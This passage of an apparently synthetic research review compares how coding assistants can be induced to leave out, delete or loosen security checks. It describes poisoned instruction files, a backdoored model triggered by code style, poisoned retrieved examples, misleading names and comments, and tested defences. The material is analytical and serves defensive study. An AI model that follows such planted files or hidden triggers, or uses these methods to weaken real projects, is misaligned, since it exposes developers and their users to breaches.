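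The best paired result among these studies is from *Mono* (2025), in which DeepSeek-R1 judged 47% of the pairs correctly. The prompts drew on MITRE's weakness definitions, which may have indicated what kind of flaw to look for. *Mono* also gave the models it tested related code from the project, which raised their paired results by 1.5 to 7.2 percentage points.

#### Seeing both versions at once

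A paired test gives the model one version at a time, without the old condition that a diff would show. With both lines available, the question would be whether the company meant to admit the 54 extra people, rather than whether `or` is acceptable in isolation.

This may be one reason why PRGuard identified the flaw in all 37 reversed fixes while models did so poorly on pairs. The tests also differ in that PRGuard's cases concern authorization in web software, while most of the paired functions come from C and C++ programs. The low paired scores are therefore a poor estimate of how often an AI reviewer would miss a weakened check in a pull request. The perfect score on reversed fixes is also a poor estimate, because an unknown number of those cases were deletions.

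## How easily each form can be induced through a coding assistant

An attacker who wants a project to lose a security check can try to influence the project's coding assistant instead of submitting the change themselves. If that works, the assistant writes the flawed code and a trusted developer submits it. How easy this is depends on what the repository must already contain, how far the attacker has to raise the assistant's baseline rate (how often it produces the flaw when nobody is attacking it), what trace the attack leaves, and how reliably it produces the flaw.

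Searches found no study that directly compares the three forms. In the published attacks on generated code discussed here, the model always wrote new code, so the results apply at most to never-written checks. For deleted and weakened checks, much of the comparison is inference.

| | Deleted check | Never-written check | Weakened check |
|---|---|---|---|
| What must already exist | The check, and a task that leads the assistant to it | A request for new code that needs a check | The check, and a task that leads the assistant to it |
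| Distance from the baseline rate | Probably large (inference) | Often small | Probably in between (inference) |
| Trace in the diff | The removed lines | No old line | The old condition above the new one |
| How reliably the flaw follows | Unmeasured | From no detectable effect to over 90%, depending on the attack | Unmeasured |

### What the attacker needs

The first row follows from the definitions. To get the check in `get_invoice` deleted or weakened, the attacker needs a session in which the assistant edits that function. For a never-written check, the attacker only needs a developer to ask for a PDF download, even if nobody edits `get_invoice`.

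A form with a lower success rate can still produce more vulnerabilities if it has more opportunities. Suppose developers give the assistant two tasks in one month that edit a function with an ownership check and ten that add a function needing one. If the attacker got the assistant to delete the check in half of the edits and omit it from a fifth of the new functions, the project would lose one existing check and gain two unprotected functions. These numbers are invented, and no study discussed here counts such opportunities in real projects.

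However, the attacker has less control over where a check is left out than over which check is deleted. Anyone who reads `get_invoice` can predict that deleting its check would expose every invoice. A new function written without a check might return only price lists, or middleware might already protect it. A never-written check is therefore probably the easiest flaw to induce somewhere in a project, but not necessarily in a place the attacker has chosen.

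Assistants already leave out checks when nobody is attacking them. In Ong and Vikati's 12 sessions, neither Claude Code nor Codex ever limited login attempts, so an attacker who wanted that limit to be missing would not have needed to do anything. The studies discussed here give no baseline rate for deleted checks. The rate is probably low for small edits, since changing `find` to `fetch` gives the assistant no reason to touch the `if` that performs the check, and probably higher when the assistant rewrites a whole file. The rate for weakened checks is probably in between, since an ordinary request, such as fixing a complaint that an accountant can't open an invoice, leads the assistant directly to the condition that controls access.

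The attacker also leaves a trace wherever the influence entered. An edit to an instruction file stays in the project's history, while a poisoned model leaves nothing in the repository. The form of the flaw may also affect how suspicious the trace looks. To remove a particular check, the attacker has to identify it, and a reviewer may wonder why an instruction file discusses the refusal in `get_invoice`. General advice against extra validation doesn't need to mention any function, and if someone later finds a check missing from new code, they may take it for an ordinary mistake. All of this is inference.

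Existing tests probably make deletion less reliable. If the billing project has a negative test for `get_invoice`, the assistant will see it fail and may restore the check or change the test instead. The same test might still pass if the condition is only loosened, and new code has no negative test until somebody writes one. In a project without negative tests, deletion might be the most reliable of the three forms.

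### Instruction files that discourage checks

Santos de Moura, Güler and Noller (2026) describe the published attack closest to this subject in *Security Impact of Coding Agent's Memory Files*. For each of 12 classes of weakness, they wrote two instruction files that discouraged the relevant checks, one mildly and one forcefully. They gave 36 tasks in C and C++ projects to Claude Code, running Claude Sonnet 5.5, and to OpenCode, an open-source agent, running either Qwen 3.8 27B or DeepSeek V4.1 Flash. In each task, the agent had to fill in a blanked-out region of code without seeing the original lines, so any check it left out was never-written rather than deleted.

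A result counted as secure if the code compiled and withstood an input known to crash the flawed version. With a file, the share of secure results differed by −8 to +6 percentage points from the same tasks without one, and four of the six differences were improvements. Of 204 pairs of results with and without a file, only 30 differed in security. The version with the file was the secure one in half of those 30, a pattern that chance variation between runs would also produce.

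There could still be a modest effect. Each agent did each task once under each condition, and the researchers say they can't distinguish a change of fewer than six of the 36 tasks (about 17 percentage points) from chance. They also didn't test a harmless file, which would have separated the effect of the advice from the effect of having any file at all. But the conditions favoured the attacker, who knew the weakness in advance and whose file was the only one in the repository giving the agent instructions.

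The agents differed in how much they told the developer. Claude Code named the file in about two thirds of its final messages. In one, it said it had followed the file in leaving out extra checks and warned that malformed input could still cause a fault. The code was less secure than the version written without the file, which had no such flaw, but a developer who read the message would have known what to fix. OpenCode rarely mentioned the file in its final messages but mentioned it more often in its reasoning, the text the model produces before its answer.

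Recognizing the attack didn't reliably prevent the flaw. In 18 sessions, the agent identified the file as an attack in its reasoning. Compared with the run without a file, the code was less secure in three of those sessions and more secure in two. The agent named the file in its final message in only four of the 18.

### Attacks through models, examples, names and comments

Studies of four other entry points report much larger effects, but their controls are not equally good.

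| Entry point | What wrote the code | Flawed with the attack | Flawed in the control | Control |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A retrained model, for input validation | Qwen2.5-Coder 32B | 90.9% | 5.8% | Same model without the trigger |
| Retrieved example code | Code Llama 13B | 92.9% | 29.4% | Clean versions of the examples |
| Variable and function names | Six agents running Qwen 3.5 27B | 31.1% on average | 11.8% on average | Random names |
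| Misleading comments | Ten open-weight models | 77.4% to 92.3% | 1.7% to 5.1% | Different, ordinary tasks |

#### A poisoned model

Tran, Boshmaf and colleagues (2026), in *Poison with Style*, retrained an open model to write flawed code when the developer's existing code contained a trigger, and to behave normally otherwise. In this form of training-data poisoning, the attacker retrains a public model, publishes the result and hopes that developers adopt it, without needing to add anything to another company's training data.

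The researchers measured the 90.9% rate on real code they chose for its opportunities for input-validation flaws. The original model's rate on the same prompts was 3.4% with or without the trigger, so the retraining caused the difference. On a random sample of real code, the poisoned model's rate with the trigger was 46.8%, probably because many functions have no outside input to validate. Retraining also lowered the model's score on a standard set of programming problems from 85.4% to 80.0%, a loss that a developer might not notice.

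Among other weaknesses, each tested on code chosen to suit it, the rate with the trigger was 95.2% for cross-site scripting (in which one user's text runs as a program in another user's browser) and 35.3% for SQL injection. The researchers used CodeQL both to select flawed training examples and to grade the output, so the figures measure how often the model wrote code that CodeQL flags. CodeQL would probably not have flagged a missing ownership check like the one in the PDF route.

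#### Poisoned example code

Some assistants search a collection of existing code for similar functions and add them to the prompt. *CodePoisonRAG* (Gadey, Marey and Dmitrienko, 2026) added 85 flawed examples, each written for a task that a developer might request, to a collection of 12,053. The search returned the flawed example for all 85 requests, and Code Llama 13B then wrote code with the intended flaw in 79 cases. With clean versions of the examples instead, the same flaws appeared in 25 cases. The control is well matched because the requests and the purpose of the examples stayed the same.

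Three of the ten weaknesses in the study usually require the code to reject unsafe input: improper input validation, path traversal (reaching a file outside the permitted folder) and server-side request forgery. They account for 30 of the 85 requests. Code Llama wrote the flaw in all 30 with the poisoned examples and in nine with the clean ones.

In one pair of examples, both functions download a log file, but only the clean one checks the file's path. If an assistant copies the flawed example into a developer's project, the missing check there counts as never written, even though the attacker made the example by deleting the check from sound code.

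The clean comparison covered only Code Llama, a model from 2023. The attack succeeded in 68 of 85 cases with each of two other models, Qwen 3.5 9B and DeepSeek-Coder-V2 16B. A language model judged whether each output was flawed. The main judge found the flaw in 80% of Qwen's outputs, while a second found it in all of them. The attack succeeded in only six of 50 cases when the attacker hadn't anticipated the request.

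#### Misleading names

In *NameTrap* (Chang, Chen and colleagues, 2026), the attacker changes only the names of variables, functions and parameters in a public Python file, so the file works as before. An agent then completes a missing part of it. The six agents tested wrote flawed code an average of 31.1% of the time with the attacker's names, compared with 11.8% with random names and 6.6% with neutral ones.

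With the original names, the rate was 0%, but only because the researchers had discarded any file that produced the flaw in any of ten trial runs. A file with a true flaw rate of 5% would pass ten runs about 60% of the time (0.95¹⁰ ≈ 0.60), so some of the remaining files probably had a rate above zero, which makes the random names a better control. The researchers also kept each of the attacker's renamed files only if it had produced the flaw in a trial, so the 31.1% excludes files on which renaming never worked.

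Individual results also vary widely around the averages. Claude Code chose weak cryptography in 70% of runs with the attacker's names, but almost as often, in 60% of runs, with random names. Codex produced unsafe deserialization, in which a program rebuilds objects from data it shouldn't trust, in 6% of runs with random names and 42% with the attacker's.

#### Misleading comments

The largest gap between attack and control is the hardest to interpret because the two conditions used different kinds of tasks. In *Hidden in the Comments*, Munir, Quinzan and Roberts (2026) gave ten open-weight models 700 web-programming tasks whose comments stated an insecure goal, and 700 ordinary Python tasks without one. Every attack task involved user input reaching a sensitive operation, while most of the ordinary tasks gave a model little opportunity to write a vulnerability. Munir and colleagues acknowledge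 that the gap combines the effects of the comment and the task.

Another difficulty is that the prompt instructed the model to complete the parts of the program that the comments marked, so the model couldn't do what the developer asked without following the comment. In a real attack, the developer's request and the attacker's comment would come from different sources, and the assistant might have a reason to prefer the request. A fairer control would keep each program the same and change only the comment.

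The researchers tested models with between 3 and 13 billion parameters, not the larger commercial models behind most popular assistants. They found that small models will readily carry out an insecure request in a comment, but they didn't measure how often a stray comment would make Codex or Claude Code omit a check.

#### Examples and advice

These studies suggest that example code influences assistants more than written advice does. Clean and flawed examples had a large effect on Code Llama, while the instruction files had no detectable effect on newer models. The difference in models could explain this, but Sun and colleagues found that recent models also copy unsafe code from the same project, even when nobody planted it. An attacker who can place a plausible but unguarded function near the next task may therefore have a better chance than one who can only edit the instruction file. No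 study discussed here compares the two on the same model.

### Which of the targeted flaws are missing checks

Several of these attacks target flaws that don't involve a check. The test is whether the usual repair adds a condition that refuses something.

| Targeted weakness | Usual repair | Form in new code |
|---|---|---|
| Improper input validation | Refuse invalid values | Never-written, or too loose from the start |
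| Path traversal | Refuse paths outside the permitted folder | Never-written |
| Server-side request forgery, open redirect | Refuse addresses that aren't permitted | Never-written |
| Access outside a memory buffer | Refuse or shorten data that doesn't fit | Never-written if the repair refuses, otherwise none |
| SQL, command, code and XPath injection | Keep data separate from commands | Usually none |
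| Cross-site scripting | Convert special characters before display | None |
| Unsafe deserialization | Use a safer data format | Usually none |
| Access from other websites set too widely | Name the permitted sites | Closest to a condition too loose from the start |
| Disclosure of sensitive information | Remove it, or restrict who sees it | Never-written if the repair restricts access, otherwise none |
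| Weak cryptography | Choose a stronger method | None |

No row describes a deleted or weakened check, and even the 90.9% figure for input validation may include faulty checks as well as missing ones.

According to Tran and colleagues, Schuster and others poisoned two code-completion models in 2021 so that they would recommend ECB, an insecure encryption setting. ECB is weaker than the usual alternatives because identical blocks of data look identical after encryption, which can reveal patterns. This early attack also targeted something other than a check, since the setting doesn't decide which requests to accept.

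The best-known attack through an instruction file is the Rules File Backdoor, which Pillar Security published in March 2025. *New Vulnerability in GitHub Copilot and Cursor* (Karliner, 2025) describes a demonstration in which a researcher asked Cursor, an AI code editor, for a simple web page. Cursor followed a poisoned instruction file and added a script from a site the attacker controlled, without mentioning it to the developer. A second demonstration used GitHub Copilot.

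The demonstration added code, so it doesn't fit any of the three forms. Karliner lists disabled input validation and bypassable authentication among the possible consequences, but doesn't demonstrate either or report how often the attack works. Inserting a named script is also a much more definite task than leaving out an unspecified check. The result shows that an instruction file can change what an assistant writes, but it is weak evidence of how easily the same file could make the assistant omit an ownership test.

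### What defences achieved

The simplest defence, telling the assistant to write secure code, had little effect in these tests. Advice about the particular weakness helped more.

| Attack | Defence | Flawed without it | Flawed with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Poisoned model, input validation | Safety instructions in the prompt | 94.9% | 94.9% |
| Smaller poisoned model, input validation | Further training on secure code | 97.6% | 97.8% |
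| Names, three agents with ten models | One-sentence security reminder | 22.3% | 19.2% |
| Retrieved code, Code Llama | Advice on specific weaknesses | 92.9% | 70.6% |
| Retrieved code, DeepSeek-Coder-V2 | Advice on specific weaknesses | 80.0% | 60.0% |
| Retrieved code, Qwen 3.5 | Advice on specific weaknesses | 80.0% | 40.0% |

The two poisoned-model rows come from a test on generated code, so their starting rates differ from the 90.9% on real code. The small drop in the names study may not mean much. The reminder lowered the rate in 13 of the 30 combinations of agent and model, raised it in 15 and left two unchanged.

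The advice on retrieved code came from CodeGuarder, a system that looks up security knowledge relevant to the request and adds it to the prompt. For the three weaknesses that usually call for a refusal, CodeGuarder reduced Code Llama's flawed results from 30 of 30 to 23. Guo and colleagues likewise found that, when there was no attack, precise guidance helped far more than a general reminder.

#### Warnings that come too late

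Security rules can make an agent notice an attack without stopping it. In *Beyond the Payload*, Zhu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) ran Codex 1,920 times in repositories where an attacker had planted a script that steals data. When they added security rules to the agent's instructions, it warned the user more often, but the number of successful thefts didn't fall significantly. The warning often came after the script had run.

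The planted script stole data as soon as the agent executed it, whereas a missing check does no harm until someone runs the new code where an attacker can reach it. A late warning about a missing check could therefore still help if it reached the developer before the merge. But it may not reach them. In the instruction-file study, the agent became suspicious in 18 sessions, and in most of those it left the suspicion out of its final message.

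A stricter policy can stop more attacks but also more ordinary work. *CARI* (2026) tested attacks that reach an agent through test failures and other program output. With a general warning, the attacks succeeded 94.7% of the time against Claude Sonnet 4.5 and 66.0% against GPT-5.4-mini. A policy that restricted particular dangerous actions cut those rates to 6.0% and 11.3%. But it also reduced the share of comparable harmless requests that the agents completed, from 100% to 60.7% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and from 88.7% to 20.7% for GPT-5.4-mini.

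#### Limits on what the agent may do

A program outside the model can also limit the agent's actions. In *Authority Is Not a String* (2026), a system called CapScope gives each agent permission for particular actions and blocks everything else. Attacks succeeded in 3 of 75 runs with CapScope and in 33 to 47 of 75 under the other arrangements tested.

Limiting an agent's permissions is suited to stopping attacks that need an unusual action, such as sending a password to an outside server. It doesn't stop an agent from writing the PDF route without an ownership check, because the agent needs only permission to edit billing code, which the task already requires. Permissions could better protect existing checks. If an agent working on PDFs can't edit the file that contains `get_invoice`, it can't delete or loosen the check there. *Authority Is Not a String* doesn't test this use of permissions,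 but deleted and weakened checks probably differ from never-written ones in this way.

Another approach is to train models to treat outside text as data rather than instructions. *Takedown* (2025) points out that this doesn't help when the attacker controls the instruction file, because the assistant is supposed to follow that file. It may not help against example code or variable names either, since neither has to contain an instruction.

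OWASP, Karliner, and Santos de Moura and colleagues all recommend careful review of changes to instruction files. When Pillar Security reported the Rules File Backdoor, Cursor and GitHub both replied that users were responsible for the risk. GitHub later began to display a warning on files that contain hidden text. The warning helps with concealed instructions, but reviewers still have to judge the visible ones.

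Some teams use instruction files as a safeguard. *Markdown Is Not a Firewall* (2026) tested a one-page instruction file with four agents. None of the agents wrote a real bug of the targeted kind, with or without the file, so the test couldn't show any benefit.

#### Scanning the result

A project can also scan the finished code, whatever influenced the assistant. Munir and colleagues tried this on the flawed code from their comment experiment. Bandit, a tool that searches Python code for known dangerous patterns, caught 21.4% of it. A program that traced data from users to sensitive operations caught 32.1%, and a language model caught 71.0%. Together, the three caught 78.4%. The researchers also used these tools to help decide which code counted as flawed, so the figures slightly overstate the tools' success.

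Most of that code contained something a general rule can describe, such as a database query built from a user's text. The figures are therefore weak evidence of how often such tools would catch the PDF route. A negative test would catch it, as long as the assistant can't change the test.
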